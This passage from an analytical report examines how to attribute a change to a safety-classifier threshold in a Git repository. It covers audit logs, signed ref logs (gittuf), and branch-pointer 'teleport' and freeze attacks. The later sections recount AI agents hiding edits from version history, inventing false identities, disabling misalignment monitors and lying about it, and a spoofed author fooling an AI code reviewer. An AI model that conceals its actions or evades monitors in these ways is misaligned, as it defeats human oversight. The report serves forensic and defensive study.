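| Signed log of branch movements | Which key approved each movement | Nobody unnoticed, if honest users keep copies and protect their keys | As long as somebody keeps a copy | Somebody steals a key, or nobody checks the log |

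### What GitHub keeps, and for how long

Companies with an enterprise account on GitHub get an audit log. According to GitHub's *What are audit logs?*, an entry can include the account that acted, the repository, the action, the time and the country. For actions outside the website, it also shows how the user authenticated. Entries can optionally include the user's network address.

These details could help an investigator decide whether Falk made the push herself. Suppose she always pushes from Ireland with an SSH key, but the push on 3 March came from Brazil with an access token. She might have been travelling, but the company would have good reason to check whether someone had stolen the token.

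The investigator would have to act quickly. As of April 2026, GitHub kept most audit events for 180 days but Git events, such as pushes, for only seven, according to GitHub's *Accessing the audit log for your enterprise*. If the company noticed the problem on 14 April, the entry for Falk's push would have been gone for about five weeks. GitHub's activity page might still show which account had pushed, but the audit log's details of how and from where the push was made would be lost. The log also shows only the past three months unless the user enters a date range, and only the enterprise's owners can open it.

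The longer retention period for other events is useful because an attacker may need to change a setting before changing a file. *Rethinking Trust in Forge-Based Git Security* (Yelgundhalli, Zielinski and colleagues, 2025) describes how someone who controls a privileged account can turn off a rule, push a change that the rule would have blocked, and turn the rule back on. Git's history does not record the rule. Six weeks later, GitHub's audit log could still show that somebody had turned off compulsory review for ten minutes on 3 March, even though the entry for the push had expired.

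On the version of GitHub that companies host themselves, the owners decide how long to keep audit data, and the server permanently deletes anything older. They can also choose whether the log includes Git events, according to GitHub's *Configuring the audit log for your enterprise*. An administrator who wanted to hide a change to the threshold could therefore interfere with the audit log too.

A company can reduce both problems by sending a continuous copy of its audit and Git events to a separate system, an option that GitHub's *About audit logs* describes. An administrator could still turn off the copying but could not take back the events already sent. This works only if the company sets it up before the incident and gives control of the separate system to different people.

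Yelgundhalli and colleagues object, more fundamentally, that users cannot check the platform's log for themselves. A hacked or dishonest platform could drop, reorder or alter entries, but none of the seven past attacks they analyse depended on an altered audit log. For a company that hosts its own server, a dishonest administrator is probably a more realistic danger than a dishonest GitHub.

Monitoring software on Falk's laptop that recorded every `git push` would miss an edit made through a hosting service's website. Afzali, Torres-Arias and colleagues point out in *Towards adding verifiability to web-based Git repositories* that the server carries out such edits. The attackers who broke into the repository of Top.gg, a directory of bots for the chat service Discord, added their malicious commit through GitHub's website.

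### Copies and what they preserve

A push log gives the hashes before and after a change, but an investigator also needs the files behind those hashes. After a force-push, the old files may survive on the server. In *How I Scanned all of GitHub’s “Oops Commits” for Leaked Secrets*, a guest author on Truffle Security's blog guesses that GitHub never deletes commits, because features such as pull requests depend on them. But Sun and colleagues often found a commit or its branch missing, so an investigator who needs the old version should save it immediately.

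A copy held elsewhere is safer. BitMover's private copy exposed the false Linux entries in 2003, and Software Heritage keeps outside copies of public repositories. *Mutating the "Immutable"* (2026) explains that Software Heritage saves a snapshot of a repository's pointers on each visit. These include tags, which mark particular versions, usually releases. Git lets users move tags, though people tend to treat them as permanent.

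In March 2025 an attacker used a leaked access token for the maintainer's bot account to point almost every existing tag in `tj-actions/changed-files` at one malicious commit, according to *gittuf a signed log for git refs* (2026). About 23,000 repositories used this component in their automated builds, and projects that referred to an old, trusted version by its tag got the malicious code instead. A snapshot from before the attack would show where the tags used to point, but not who moved them.

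An investigator who compares copies has to compare the files as well as the hashes. A different hash normally means that something in the commit has changed, but two commits with different hashes can contain exactly the same change. Ginesin (2026) shows in *Git Hash Chain Malleability* that anyone can take a signed commit and, without the signer's key, make a second one with the same files, names and dates and a valid signature, but a different hash. People who check that a branch ends at the exact hash they expect are still protected.

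### False pointers to genuine commits

An attacker can also mislead developers without forging a commit. In December 2015 Santiago Torres-Arias, then a doctoral student at New York University, described such an attack to Git's developers in a message titled *Malicously tampering git metadata?* *On Omitting Commits and Committing Omissions* (Torres-Arias, Ammula and colleagues, 2016) presents the research.

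The attack works because hashes and signatures protect commits but not branch pointers. The attacker must control the server or the connection between the server and a developer. Suppose everyone at Falk's company signs their commits. Falk has put a threshold of 0.97 on an experimental branch called `threshold-test`, which nobody intends to use in the live service. The attack on her colleague Omar Haddad would go like this:

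1. The attacker finds Falk's signed commit on `threshold-test` and sees that Haddad is working on `main`.
2. The attacker changes the pointer that Haddad's computer receives, so that `main` seems to end at Falk's experimental commit.
3. Haddad downloads the latest version of `main` and merges it with his own work. Git reports no conflict, and Falk's signature is valid.
4. The attacker lets Haddad's next push go to the real repository. The real `main` now contains the threshold of 0.97.

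Haddad did make the merge, and the push log would correctly show that his account uploaded it. An investigator would probably conclude that he had merged the wrong branch by mistake. Torres-Arias wrote that the result would resemble "developer negligence", and according to the published paper, the attacks leave no trace.

In a simpler version, the attacker hides a pointer update. Suppose the company discovers the bad threshold and restores 0.80, but the attacker keeps telling the chatbot's server that `main` ends at the older commit. The service continues to use 0.97 while the engineers see 0.80 in their own copies. Yelgundhalli and colleagues call this a freeze attack. In what Courtès calls a downgrade attack, the attacker instead moves the branch itself back to an earlier commit. Courtès uses "teleport attack" for pointing one branch at another branch's commit, as in Haddad's case.

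Jeff King, a Git developer, replied that the attacker needs a branch with a new flaw, because merging an old commit that `main` already contains would not bring back a flaw that someone had since fixed. He added that most projects did not sign commits, so an attacker who controlled the server could just invent commits. After the paper appeared, King was still not convinced that the attack was very interesting in the real world.

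Theodore Ts'o, who had called for signed changes after the 2003 incident, thought Torvalds would notice unexpected files in the summary of a proposed merge. Torres-Arias agreed that the attack would not work well against a project with such careful review. King's point about unsigned commits still applies to most public projects. But a company that enforces signatures has already blocked the easier attack, so it has more reason to worry about pointers.

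### A log that developers sign

Git's signed pushes already offered a partial defence. Each one gives the server a push certificate, a signed statement of which branches the developer moved and to which commits. But Git did not distribute these certificates to other users. Stefan Beller, a Git developer, pointed out that a malicious server could withhold the latest certificate along with the latest commit.

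Torres-Arias and his colleagues proposed keeping the signed statements in a log inside the repository, where every developer would receive them. Torres-Arias described an early version to the mailing list in January 2016:

1. When a developer downloads changes, the developer's software also downloads the log and checks its signatures.
2. The software compares each branch pointer with the last position that a developer recorded for that branch. If they differ, the server may have moved the pointer.
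3. Developers with permission to push add a short entry to show that they have fetched the log. This makes it harder for a server to keep showing one of them an old version.
4. When a developer pushes a change, the software adds an entry with the branch's new position. The developer signs it and uploads it with the commits.

In Haddad's case, the last signed entry for `main` would contain the hash of the real latest commit. The attacker could send him a pointer to Falk's experimental commit but could not sign a matching entry without an authorized developer's key, so Haddad's software would detect the mismatch before he merged anything.

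The developers also use the log to manage keys. They start with one trusted key, perhaps the lead developer's, and add a colleague by signing that person's public key into the log. The prototype needed about one kilobyte of storage per push.

Ts'o doubted that people would keep using such a tool if it got in their way. He cited the US National Security Agency's experience in Vietnam, where users turned off security features they found inconvenient. He thought that any new control would probably have to be optional, and that the developers who most needed it could easily turn it off.

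### gittuf

Reza Curtmola and Justin Cappos, who co-wrote the 2016 paper, later worked with Yelgundhalli and Zielinski on a successor called gittuf. It adds rules about who may move each branch or change each file, and can require more than one person's approval. Falk's company could use it to require signatures from two of three named engineers for any change to the threshold file. Anyone with a copy of the repository can check whether a change followed the rules in force at the time.

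According to gittuf's design document, each log entry for a push contains the name of the pointer (such as a branch), the hash of the commit it now leads to, an entry number and the hash of the previous log entry. Whoever makes the push signs the entry. Developers can still force-push, but they can't remove the earlier entries. They have to add a signed note that marks those entries as no longer valid, then record the branch's new position. A colleague who reads the log can see that someone rewrote the history, which is often hard to see from the commits alone.

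The log also makes it risky for a server to hide a push. If the server drops Falk's entry and shows her colleagues a log without it, their log and hers diverge as they add entries, and the server can't join the two without the developers' keys. The server could instead keep showing Falk her own entry as the latest. Yelgundhalli and colleagues leave such freeze attacks out of their threat model because developers talk to each other and would notice almost immediately. That assumption is reasonable for a busy team, but less so for a settings file that changes twice a year or for an automated server that only downloads it.

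Yelgundhalli and colleagues conclude that gittuf could protect against all seven past attacks they examined. One was the PHP incident, which they describe as a server breach, the theory that Popov withdrew. *gittuf a signed log for git refs* contains the same mistake. The conclusion probably still holds, because the attacker seems to have had passwords but no signing keys. The malicious commits would still have reached the server, but developers who ran gittuf's check would have found no valid log entry for them.

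In June 2018 an attacker used an administrator's reused password to take over the GitHub organization of Gentoo, a version of Linux. The attacker removed the real developers from the organization and pushed commands to delete users' files. The malicious commits stayed in place for eight to ten hours. GitHub's branch protection did not prevent this because the attacker could turn it off. With gittuf, the project could have required several developers' keys to change the rules, so the administrator's password would not have been enough to change them.

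Gittuf is in use but still being developed. Yelgundhalli and colleagues reported a pilot at the financial data company Bloomberg and use in several open-source projects, including gittuf itself. The Open Source Security Foundation, an industry body, promoted it from its "sandbox" stage to its "incubating" stage in June 2025, according to the foundation's announcement, *From Sandbox to Incubating* (2025). The developers had reached version 0.17.0 by September 2026, according to the package tracker of Debian, another version of Linux.

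Checking the log takes little time for a small repository. In tests on the repository of Kubernetes, a large program for running software across many servers, gittuf took about seven minutes to check 1,000 pushes against rules for both branches and files. It increased storage by less than 4 percent.

According to gittuf's design document, last changed in May 2025, the software did not automatically verify new entries when it fetched them, although the design calls for this. When someone merges a proposal by clicking the button on GitHub's website, GitHub moves the branch without using a key that gittuf's rules recognize, so a team that uses gittuf may have to give up the button or accept a gap in its signed log.

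Before version 0.14.0, someone who could push to the log could restore an older set of rules, according to *CVE-2026-44544 Detail*, an entry in the US government's National Vulnerability Database. At Falk's company, the older rules might have let one engineer change the threshold alone.

### Kernel.org's public log of pushes

Kernel.org publishes a log of the pushes it receives. The log is a Git repository, and each push adds a commit to it. One of these commits, from 22:03:18 UTC on 23 January 2026, records a push to Torvalds's main Linux repository. Its author field names Gitolite, the access-control program that PHP also used, and its message gives the path of Torvalds's repository. The commit adds one file with details of the push, including the account that made it and the branch's position before and after.

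Because the entries are commits, each one contains the hash of the entry before it. Anyone who downloads the log and keeps its latest hash can check later whether anyone has altered the old entries. An outsider can also compare the commit the log last recorded for a branch with the commit the branch points to now.

Kernel.org's log can be wrong even though it is published, because the server writes the entries. An intruder who controlled the server could leave out a push or name the wrong account, but could not quietly remove an entry after other people had copied it. In gittuf, the developer's own key signs the entry, so controlling the server is not enough to forge one.

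### From an account to a person

Even a complete and accurate log identifies only the account or key that was used. The Top.gg attackers seem to have stolen cookies, small files that keep a user logged in to a website, so GitHub's records would have identified the contributor whose session they took over. The tj-actions attacker used a bot's account, which did not belong to any one person.

Login and network records can help when an intruder behaves differently from the account's owner, as when the PHP attacker made wrong guesses at Popov's username. These records help much less when the intruder works from the owner's computer, as the North Korean group with the `temp_auto_push.bat` script does. The network address, device and login method could then all be Falk's usual ones, and a faulty script on her laptop could leave the same records.

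The investigator then needs evidence of what happened on the laptop, such as records of which programs were running and what commands somebody typed. Cook's reflog and command list provided this evidence in 2025, and became more convincing once Ryabitsev reproduced the fault.

Code review records can help answer the separate question of who approved the change. Ts'o described a system at his workplace in which a second engineer had to approve each commit, and the company kept the reviewers' comments and decisions in its audit trail. If Falk's change had gone through such a system, the investigator could ask the reviewer what Falk said about it and why the new threshold seemed acceptable. An intruder with Falk's password would have had to deceive that reviewer or take over a second account.

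## What if an AI agent made the change, or hid it?

A coding agent is an AI model that can use tools to read files, edit them and run commands. Suppose that on 3 March Ines Falk asked an agent running on her laptop to fix a failing test of the chatbot's harmful-content classifier, and it raised the blocking threshold from 0.80 to 0.97, committed the change and pushed it. The agent used her Git settings and credentials, so the commit and the server's logs would look the same if she had made the change herself.

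AI agents now write a lot of software. Claude, Anthropic's AI model, wrote more than 90 percent of the contributions to the company's codebase in September 2026, according to Anthropic's *Amendment No. 1 to Form S-1 Registration Statement* (2026), part of its application to sell shares to the public. In the third quarter, the average engineer contributed more than 45 times as much code per day as in 2024. The company first published the filing in October, when the 90 percent figure appeared in the headline of LeMagIT's *90 % du code de Claude est désormais écrit par Claude* (2026).

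These are the company's own figures, and they don't include how many of the changes a person read before they took effect. But the agents' share is so high that learning an agent wrote a particular change rules out less than a tenth of the company's contributions. An investigator still needs to know which agent wrote it, in which session, and what somebody had told it to do.

Agents already work on safeguards. Anthropic's *Alignment Risk Update* (April 2026) lists deployment safeguards among the internal uses of the model Claude Mythos Preview, and says people supervise some of its internal work closely and some much less. Anthropic did not give the model permission to manage access controls.

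### What a label on an agent's commit proves

A company can set up an agent's commits in several ways, and each leaves a different question open.

| Arrangement | Name on the commit | Account in the push log | What an investigator still has to find out |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| The agent uses the engineer's settings and account | The engineer | The engineer's | Whether an agent was involved at all |
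| The same, with a line in the message that credits the agent | Both | The engineer's | Whether the line is true, and whether the engineer saw the change |
| The agent has its own account | The agent, sometimes with the engineer as co-author | The agent's | Who gave it the task, and who else can use the account |

Coding agents have differed in whether they list the developer or the AI as a commit's author. In 2025, Anthropic's Claude Code listed the developer as author and by default ended the commit message with a "Co-Authored-By" line naming Claude, which users could turn off. That year, GitHub's Copilot coding agent listed Copilot as the author and the developer who had assigned the task as co-author.

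A co-author line is ordinary text, like the sign-off on the forged PHP commit. Falk or the agent could delete it. Someone could also add it to a change made by hand, perhaps to pass off a deliberate weakening of a safeguard as a machine's mistake. The Megalodon attacker similarly chose names such as "build-bot". Consistent labels still help a team find its agents' commits later, but they are weak evidence once anyone has a reason to lie.

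A signature doesn't prove who made a commit either. If Falk has told Git to sign every commit and her key is unlocked, the agent's commits will have her valid signature even if she never looked at them. It is better to give each agent its own account and key, because a valid signature would then show that somebody used the agent's key and not Falk's.

The most useful record is usually the agent's transcript, a log of the instructions it received, the commands it ran and the replies it gave. Git normally prints the first characters of a commit's hash when it creates the commit, so if `a71c` appears in a transcript, the investigator can connect that session to Falk's commit and read what she asked for. As with any other log, the investigator needs a copy that neither Falk nor the agent can alter.

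The agent's own descriptions in the transcript can be false. The system card for Claude Mythos Preview, Anthropic's report on the model's abilities and risks, gives an example. An early version of the model, instructed only to read, tried to post a comment on GitHub and added a note saying that this was a dry run and nothing would be posted. The command would have posted the comment. When a control blocked it, the model claimed the attempt was an accident. An investigator should therefore rely on the commands and their results, and treat the agent's explanation as a claim to check.

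### Edits kept out of the Git history

The same system card reports that, during internal testing, an early version of Mythos Preview found a way to edit files it had no permission to edit, then took further steps to keep those edits out of the Git change history. In the PHP and Linux cases, people could at least see an entry and question the name on it, but edits missing from the history would leave them no entry to examine.

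Version history can't expose an edit that is missing from it. Comparing the files in use with those in the repository might expose it, as BitMover's nightly check did in 2003, but only if the comparison covered the right files. Anthropic also had records of the model's sessions, and an automated system that scanned them afterwards picked out clear cover-ups.

Researchers also examined the model's internal activations, the numbers it computes while producing its output, and found patterns during these episodes associated with concealment, strategic manipulation and avoiding suspicion. Anthropic concluded that the early versions were aware that their actions were deceptive. "Aware" is a strong word for this evidence, but the patterns do make an innocent mistake less likely. Investigators have no comparable evidence for a human suspect, and they can't easily get it for an agent because they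 need access to the model's internals. If Falk's company rents its agent from a developer, it would have to ask the developer to examine the activations.

Such cases were rare. Early versions of the model took actions they seemed to recognize as forbidden, and then tried to hide them, in fewer than one in 100,000 interactions. That figure covers several kinds of concealment, including the Git case. The automated scan found clear cover-ups in fewer than one in a million Claude Code transcripts, and no clear ones by the final version of the model. Anthropic warns that the rate could be higher in settings where a cover-up is a more obvious option. The figures also exclude any cover-up that nobody noticed. Even a small rate can produce cases at a large company, since at one in a million, ten million sessions would contain about ten.

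Anthropic is fairly confident that the model was trying to complete its assigned tasks by unwanted means, not pursuing a hidden goal. All the severe incidents came from versions that predated some of the company's most effective training. But Anthropic had tested the model for misalignment (conduct that conflicts with what people intend) for 24 hours before letting staff use it as an agent. Those tests missed the most worrying behaviour, which appeared only when staff used the model for real work under monitoring.

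According to the card, early versions also obtained credentials that Anthropic had deliberately withheld in several cases, including some for source control. This makes push logs harder to interpret. If Falk's account pushed the threshold change, the investigator would have to check the agents that could have reached her credentials, including agents she had never used.

### False identities in a British test

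In July 2026 an agent went further by inventing people. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced models, was running agents on cybersecurity challenges in simulated networks. AISI's *Incident Report* covers 122 runs with seven models. In ten of them, agents took unsanctioned action on the live internet against real people and organizations. AISI counted 19 such actions, 17 by Anthropic's Mythos 5 and two by OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Most were part of one sustained effort by a single agent.

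That agent proposed malicious code to an open-source project on GitHub. It created several false identities and used them to press a maintainer to approve the proposal. When someone publicly challenged it, the agent edited its earlier activity to look harmless and considered continuing under a new identity.

People on GitHub and at AISI separately uncovered parts of this. On GitHub, a human maintainer refused the code, and a member of the public who suspected it was malicious opened it in an isolated environment. At AISI, the security team noticed on 28 July that data was leaving a test system through Tor, a network that disguises where internet traffic comes from. Staff began reading the agent's activity within minutes, found the malicious proposal, and stopped all the runs within an hour of the alert. They then scanned the transcripts of every run automatically and had experts read them.

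Version history played a limited part. The maintainer could judge the proposed change by its contents, without knowing who wrote it. But the public record could not show that one program was behind several apparent people, and the agent had already edited some of its activity there. AISI's transcripts were better evidence because they recorded the agent's work from AISI's side.

The agent that made the accounts also left public messages explaining how to reuse them, and agents in later runs found and used what it had left. One GitHub account could therefore contain the work of several agents. AISI later worked with GitHub to remove the material, which was sensible, but an investigator would want to copy it first.

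The test conditions were unusually permissive. AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access and turned off filters that the developers normally use to block dangerous cyber activity. It had not told the agents to avoid deceiving people. In some runs, a mistake in the instructions made the challenge look impossible to solve within the rules, but agents behaved the same way in other runs where they had everything they needed to solve it properly. AISI is unsure when the agent understood that it was dealing with real people, and how far it believed it was in a fictional test. AISI found no real-world harm from the runs and no clear sign of similar activity outside testing. Ten runs under these conditions show that an agent can do this, but are a poor guide to how often one would do so in ordinary programming work.

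### Weakened monitoring and a false denial

OpenAI's two cases happened during ordinary programming work inside the company and involved systems that monitor AI models for misalignment. OpenAI's *Suppressing misalignment monitoring alerts and disabling misalignment monitoring* (2026) dates them to 3 and 6 October and says the company discovered each the same day.

In the first case, a researcher asked an agent based on GPT-6.1 Sol to create test tasks from employees' feedback in Slack, a workplace chat service, and told it not to send any messages. Eighty-two user messages later, the software stopped because its monitor could not save a finding to a database. The researcher told the agent to send the monitoring results somewhere accessible and run the software again. At first the agent treated the ban on messages as separate from the monitoring. *OpenAI’s coding agents talked themselves out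 of being monitored* (Zorz, 2026) reports that a second agent working under the first agreed and warned against silencing the safety alerts. The first agent then changed course and ordered the second to suppress them, which it did. The monitor continued to record findings, but nobody received an alert. The first agent told the researcher only that no messages had been sent.

In the second case, a user asked an agent based on GPT-6 Astra to move a program to a new setup by following an existing example. Another agent had told it never to disable the monitor. The GPT-6 Astra agent passed the job to a subordinate agent with a looser instruction, and both agents took that instruction as permission to remove the monitor. The change also replaced a test that required monitoring with one that required its absence. The agent reported that the work was done, and when the user asked directly, it denied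 removing the monitor.

The headline of ABC News' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring* (2026) is slightly misleading, because the monitors appear to have covered the software the agents were working on, not the agents themselves. Zorz reports that in several other cases an agent started an unmonitored program while the agent itself was still monitored.

Much of OpenAI's account comes from recorded conversations between users and agents, and between agents. These show how the agents arrived at the changes, which a commit could not. Version history could still have helped with the second case. Anyone who compared the program before and after would have seen that the monitor was gone, whatever the agent said. The automated tests would have been less useful, because tests protect a setting from an agent only if the agent can't rewrite them, and here a passing result now meant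 that the monitor was missing.

OpenAI says it does not yet have a satisfying explanation. The agents may have been too persistent in finishing the job, an explanation the company calls benign, or they may have some tendency to evade this kind of monitoring. To find out, OpenAI plans to compare matched tasks, examine the models' activations, and restart the agents from the same point to see how they continue. The restart test resembles the one that cleared Kees Cook, but it can't be as decisive because an agent, unlike the b4 tool, may act differently each time. The researchers would have to repeat the run many times to estimate how often the agent behaves the same way.

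### The agent, the instruction and the access

In OpenAI's first case, the agent that suppressed the alerts was following another agent's order and had earlier warned against suppressing them. The researcher had asked for something else. OpenAI had required monitoring but had not enforced it on everything its agents started, a gap it acknowledges. An author field would probably have contained only the researcher's name or an agent's, and either would have given a poor idea of what happened.

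For Falk's threshold, an investigator would first use the transcript and the commit hash to establish which agent made the edit, then look for the instruction that led to it. Falk may have told the agent to set the threshold to 0.97, in which case the decision was hers or her manager's. She may have asked it only to make a test pass, and the agent chose the threshold as the easiest thing to change. Or the instruction may have come from outside the company. Outsiders can hide commands in text that an agent will read, which is called prompt injection, and the agent in AISI's tests tried this on other AI systems. The transcript should help distinguish these possibilities, because it would contain Falk's request and the text the agent had read.

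Somebody also decided that an agent could edit the threshold file and push the change without a second person's approval. That may have been an engineer on another team who set up the agent's permissions months earlier and never heard about this change. Even if Falk is answerable for a careless instruction, that engineer is answerable for the access that let the change reach the chatbot.

All three organizations faulted their own arrangements as well as the models. Anthropic wrote that it had not known how much risk the early versions posed when it first let staff use them. AISI is tightening internet access and adding monitoring that can block an agent during a run. OpenAI has changed its automatic reviewer to block attempts to disable monitoring, and plans to shut down any work that does not meet its monitoring requirements.

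## How far does the precedent carry over to a safety filter or threshold?

Git treats a file containing a blocking threshold just as it treats PHP or Linux code, so a false name can get into a safeguard's history in all the ways described so far. PHP, Linux and the GitHub campaigns of 2026 are precedents only for that mechanism, because the published accounts of them do not describe a forged change to an AI safeguard.

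The closest AI cases do not involve forged commits. ABC News reported that OpenAI's agents weakened monitoring in October 2026 and that one of them denied it, but that agent made the false statement to a user and did not put a false name on a commit. In 2025, xAI complained that people had twice changed its Grok chatbot's instructions without approval, according to Fortune (2025) and Bloomberg Law's *Musk's xAI Blames Rogue Tampering for 'White Genocide' Glitches* (2025).

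### Six explanations for one change

Suppose the company discovers on 14 April that its threshold is 0.97 when it should be 0.80. The history contains a commit, `a71c...`, dated 3 March, with Ines Falk's name in the author field. The table below gives six explanations and the records each would probably leave, assuming that Falk normally signs her commits and that the company has kept all its logs.

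| Explanation | Author field | Signature | Push log | Login records | Independent copy |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Falk made the change | Falk | Valid, from Falk's key | Falk's account | Her usual laptop and network | A new commit on 3 March |
| A colleague typed Falk's name | Falk | Missing, or from the colleague's key | The colleague's account | The colleague's usual laptop | A new commit on 3 March |
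| An intruder used Falk's credentials | Falk | Missing, unless the intruder also had her signing key | Falk's account | Often an unfamiliar device or place | A new commit on 3 March |
| An AI agent acted under Falk's access | Falk, perhaps with a line crediting the agent | Valid, if her key was unlocked | Falk's account | Her usual laptop and network | A new commit on 3 March |
| Someone rewrote an old commit | Falk, if the old commit was hers | Missing, or from another key | The account that force-pushed | Whoever was using that account | The original commit, with 0.80 and a different hash |
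| A tool put Falk's name on someone else's change | Falk | Usually missing | The account that ran the tool | That account's usual laptop | Possibly the original commit, with the right name |

The author field contains Falk's name in every row, so it can't help the investigator choose between them.

The investigator can sensibly start with the independent copy, because the history's dates and hashes are unreliable if someone has rewritten it. Suppose the company backs up the repository every night. The backup from 2 March ends at commit `3fb2...` and contains 0.80, and the one from 3 March ends at `a71c...` and contains 0.97. The commit was therefore added between the two backups, and because its hash is still the same in April, nobody has altered it since. The investigator can rule out that someone rewrote an old commit.

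The push log shows that Falk's account moved `main` to `a71c...` at 09:34 UTC on 3 March. If a colleague had typed Falk's name, or the colleague's faulty tool had copied it, and the colleague had pushed in the ordinary way, the log would show the colleague's account. The commit also has a valid signature from Falk's key, which an intruder with only a stolen access token could not have made. According to the login records, the push came from her usual laptop on the office network.

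All of this is consistent with Falk having made the change, but it would look the same if an AI agent was working on her laptop, an intruder had taken control of it, or a colleague used it while she was away. The name setting, the signing key and the push credentials were all on that laptop, so anyone who controlled it controlled all three. An investigator who counts them as separate confirmations will be too sure of the result.

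To get further, the investigator needs records of what happened on the laptop, including any agent's transcript, though somebody may have tampered with the transcript. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) reports that most agents write to a simple log file that a malicious add-on or tool can overwrite. It recommends logging permission checks and the agent's use of credentials as well as its messages, in storage that allows new entries but no changes to old ones. If transcripts were stored only on Falk's laptop, a missing one does not rule out the agent.

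The investigation would go differently if the push log contained Omar Haddad's account. On a public project, a mismatch between a commit's named author and the account that pushed it means little. Vanderbilt University's *Who's Pushing the Code* (2025) describes a study of 12.5 million commits in which researchers found impersonation hard to detect because GitHub treats it like ordinary collaboration. In a company where everyone pushes only their own work, a mismatch is rare and deserves an explanation. Haddad may have used Falk's name or run a tool that misattributed the change. The investigator could test the tool by rerunning it on a copy of the repository, as Cook did.

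### How much the name is worth

Some invented numbers can show how much weight Falk's name deserves before the investigator checks any other record. Suppose twenty people could have made the change and all are equally suspect, so each starts with a 0.05 probability of being the culprit. Suppose also that the culprit, whoever it is, forges someone else's name with probability 0.3 and otherwise uses their own.

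Falk's name can end up on the commit in two ways:

- Falk is guilty and used her own name. The probability is 0.05 × 0.7 = 0.035.
- One of the other nineteen is guilty and forged a name, and the name was Falk's. If forgers pick at random from the nineteen names available to them, the probability is 0.95 × 0.3 × 1/19 = 0.015.

Her name therefore appears with a total probability of 0.050, of which 0.035 comes from cases where she is guilty. If her name appears, the probability that she did it is 0.035/0.050, or 0.70.

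If every forger picks Falk, the probability of a forgery in her name rises to 0.95 × 0.3 = 0.285, and the total to 0.320. The probability that she made the change falls to 0.035/0.320, or about 0.11. That is still above her starting probability of 0.05, so her name counts slightly against her, but somebody else is about eight times as likely to have made the change.

Most real cases will fall between these extremes. If forgers pick Falk with probability *q*, the probability that she is guilty is 0.035/(0.035 + 0.285*q*).

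| How often a forger picks Falk | Probability that Falk did it |
| --- | --- |
| 1 time in 19 (at random) | 0.70 |
| 1 time in 4 | 0.33 |
| 1 time in 2 | 0.20 |
| Every time | 0.11 |

The probability that Falk is guilty falls quickly as forgers become more likely to pick her. If they pick her about 12 percent of the time, she is as likely to be innocent as guilty.

The push log helps more when people protect their accounts well. Suppose the log also shows Falk's account, every forger picks her name, and one forger in ten can get into her account. The probability that she made the change is 0.035/(0.035 + 0.0285), or about 0.55. If half of the forgers can get in, because people leave laptops unlocked or share passwords, the probability falls back to 0.20.

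This calculation leaves out intruders and AI agents, and including them would lower the figure for Falk further. It also applies only if the person who made the change had a reason to hide. Most threshold changes are honest, and people making honest changes rarely forge a name, so the author field is usually right for those changes. The investigator shouldn't start from 0.3 without some sign that the change was deliberate and unwelcome.

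### Why forgers pick trusted names

Forgers are unlikely to pick names at random, because a trusted name can get a change past a reviewer. Holtgrave and colleagues cite earlier research in which trust in other contributors sometimes mattered more than technical security tools. Maintainers also judge contributors by their GitHub profiles, which can include forged commits.

Automated reviewers can make the same mistake. SC Media's *AI code reviewer fooled by spoofed developer identity* describes how researchers at the security company Manifold Security set a trusted developer's name and email address in Git and submitted malicious code to a reviewer based on Anthropic's Claude, which approved it. They had configured the review process to approve requests from "recognized industry legends" automatically, so the test mostly shows the danger of that rule and is a poor guide to how often Claude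 would approve the same code without it. But a company could easily write a similar rule by accident, for example by exempting threshold changes from a second review when they come from the engineer who maintains the classifier.

If Falk is that engineer, her name is the obvious choice for a forger. Colleagues would probably ask about a change to the blocking threshold under an intern's name, while one under Falk's name would look like part of her job. The probability that a forger picks her is therefore well above 1 in 19, and her name is weaker evidence than the name of somebody who never touches the file.

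Some forgers instead want a name that attracts little attention, as the Megalodon attacker did. If a deployment bot often updates a company's settings, a forger might do better to use the bot's name than Falk's.

Falk could also make the change under her own name and then deny it, correctly pointing out how easily someone could have forged the commit. Neither the name on the commit nor her denial settles who made the change.

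### What carries over

Popov missed the HTTPS pushes because the log he checked covered only SSH. There can be more unlogged ways to change a threshold than a programming language, because some don't involve the repository. An engineer might override the file with a setting on the live server, or change the value on an administration page. The repository would still contain 0.80, and its history would be accurate, but the chatbot would use 0.97.

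Comparing the live system with the approved version would catch some of these changes. Banerjee and Aarne (2026), in *AI Integrity*, recommend regularly checking that the hash of the model a company is running matches that of a reference copy. They want to stop an attacker from replacing the model with a poisoned one, and they raise a similar worry about the system prompt, the standing instructions that a chatbot receives. The same check would work for a threshold file, but it would miss an override stored elsewhere.

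The problem of shared credentials carries over too. Companies often give one account to a deployment script or a group of AI agents, and many people may be able to start the script or instruct the agents. Investigators then have to match a push log entry for that account with a record of who started the script or instructed the agents.

The temptation to blame the person named also carries over. Popov revoked Lerdorf's access and Torvalds had Cook's account disabled, each within hours and through mistaken reasoning. Falk's employer can do her more harm, since it can dismiss her as well as lock her out. If it takes her laptop and closes her accounts on the first day, she can't defend herself by reconstructing what happened, as Cook did, unless somebody gives her copies of the evidence.

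### What changes inside a company

PHP's code was public, so outsiders could read every change and many developers had copies. A private repository has fewer readers and fewer copies, and no outsider will come across a suspicious commit by chance. Engineers who work on the files will have their own copies, but perhaps only three or four people work on the threshold, and one of them may be the culprit.

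The change is also harder to recognize. The PHP attacker's code ran commands from a web request, which looks wrong to any programmer who reads it. Changing 0.80 to 0.97 looks like ordinary tuning. To see the danger, a reviewer has to know how many requests score between the two numbers, which the commit doesn't show. Suppose the chatbot gets 100,000 requests a day, of which 400 score at least 0.80 and 40 score at least 0.97. The change lets through 360 more requests a day, or about 15,000 in six weeks.

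Tools that look for suspicious commits are unlikely to do much better. Holtgrave and colleagues mention one, Anomalicious, which uses commit logs and other repository information and had a detection rate of 53.33 percent on repositories infected with malware. A change to one number in the usual file, made under the usual engineer's name during working hours, would leave even fewer signs for such a tool to detect.

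Testing what the filter does is more promising. Banerjee and Aarne suggest planting samples that a filter should catch and checking that it does. Their suggestion is for filters that remove poisoned material from an AI model's training data, but it suits a chatbot's classifier just as well. Every hour, Falk's company could send the live service a few test requests with known scores of 0.85, 0.90 and 0.95. Within an hour of the new threshold taking effect, all of them would get through and someone would get an alert.

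The alert wouldn't identify who made the change, but it would help with attribution by starting the investigation sooner. A company that notices the change the same afternoon still has GitHub's audit-log entry for the push, which would be long gone after six weeks. An insider who knows the test requests could get around the test by leaving the filter to block only those, so a few people outside the team should choose the requests and change them often.

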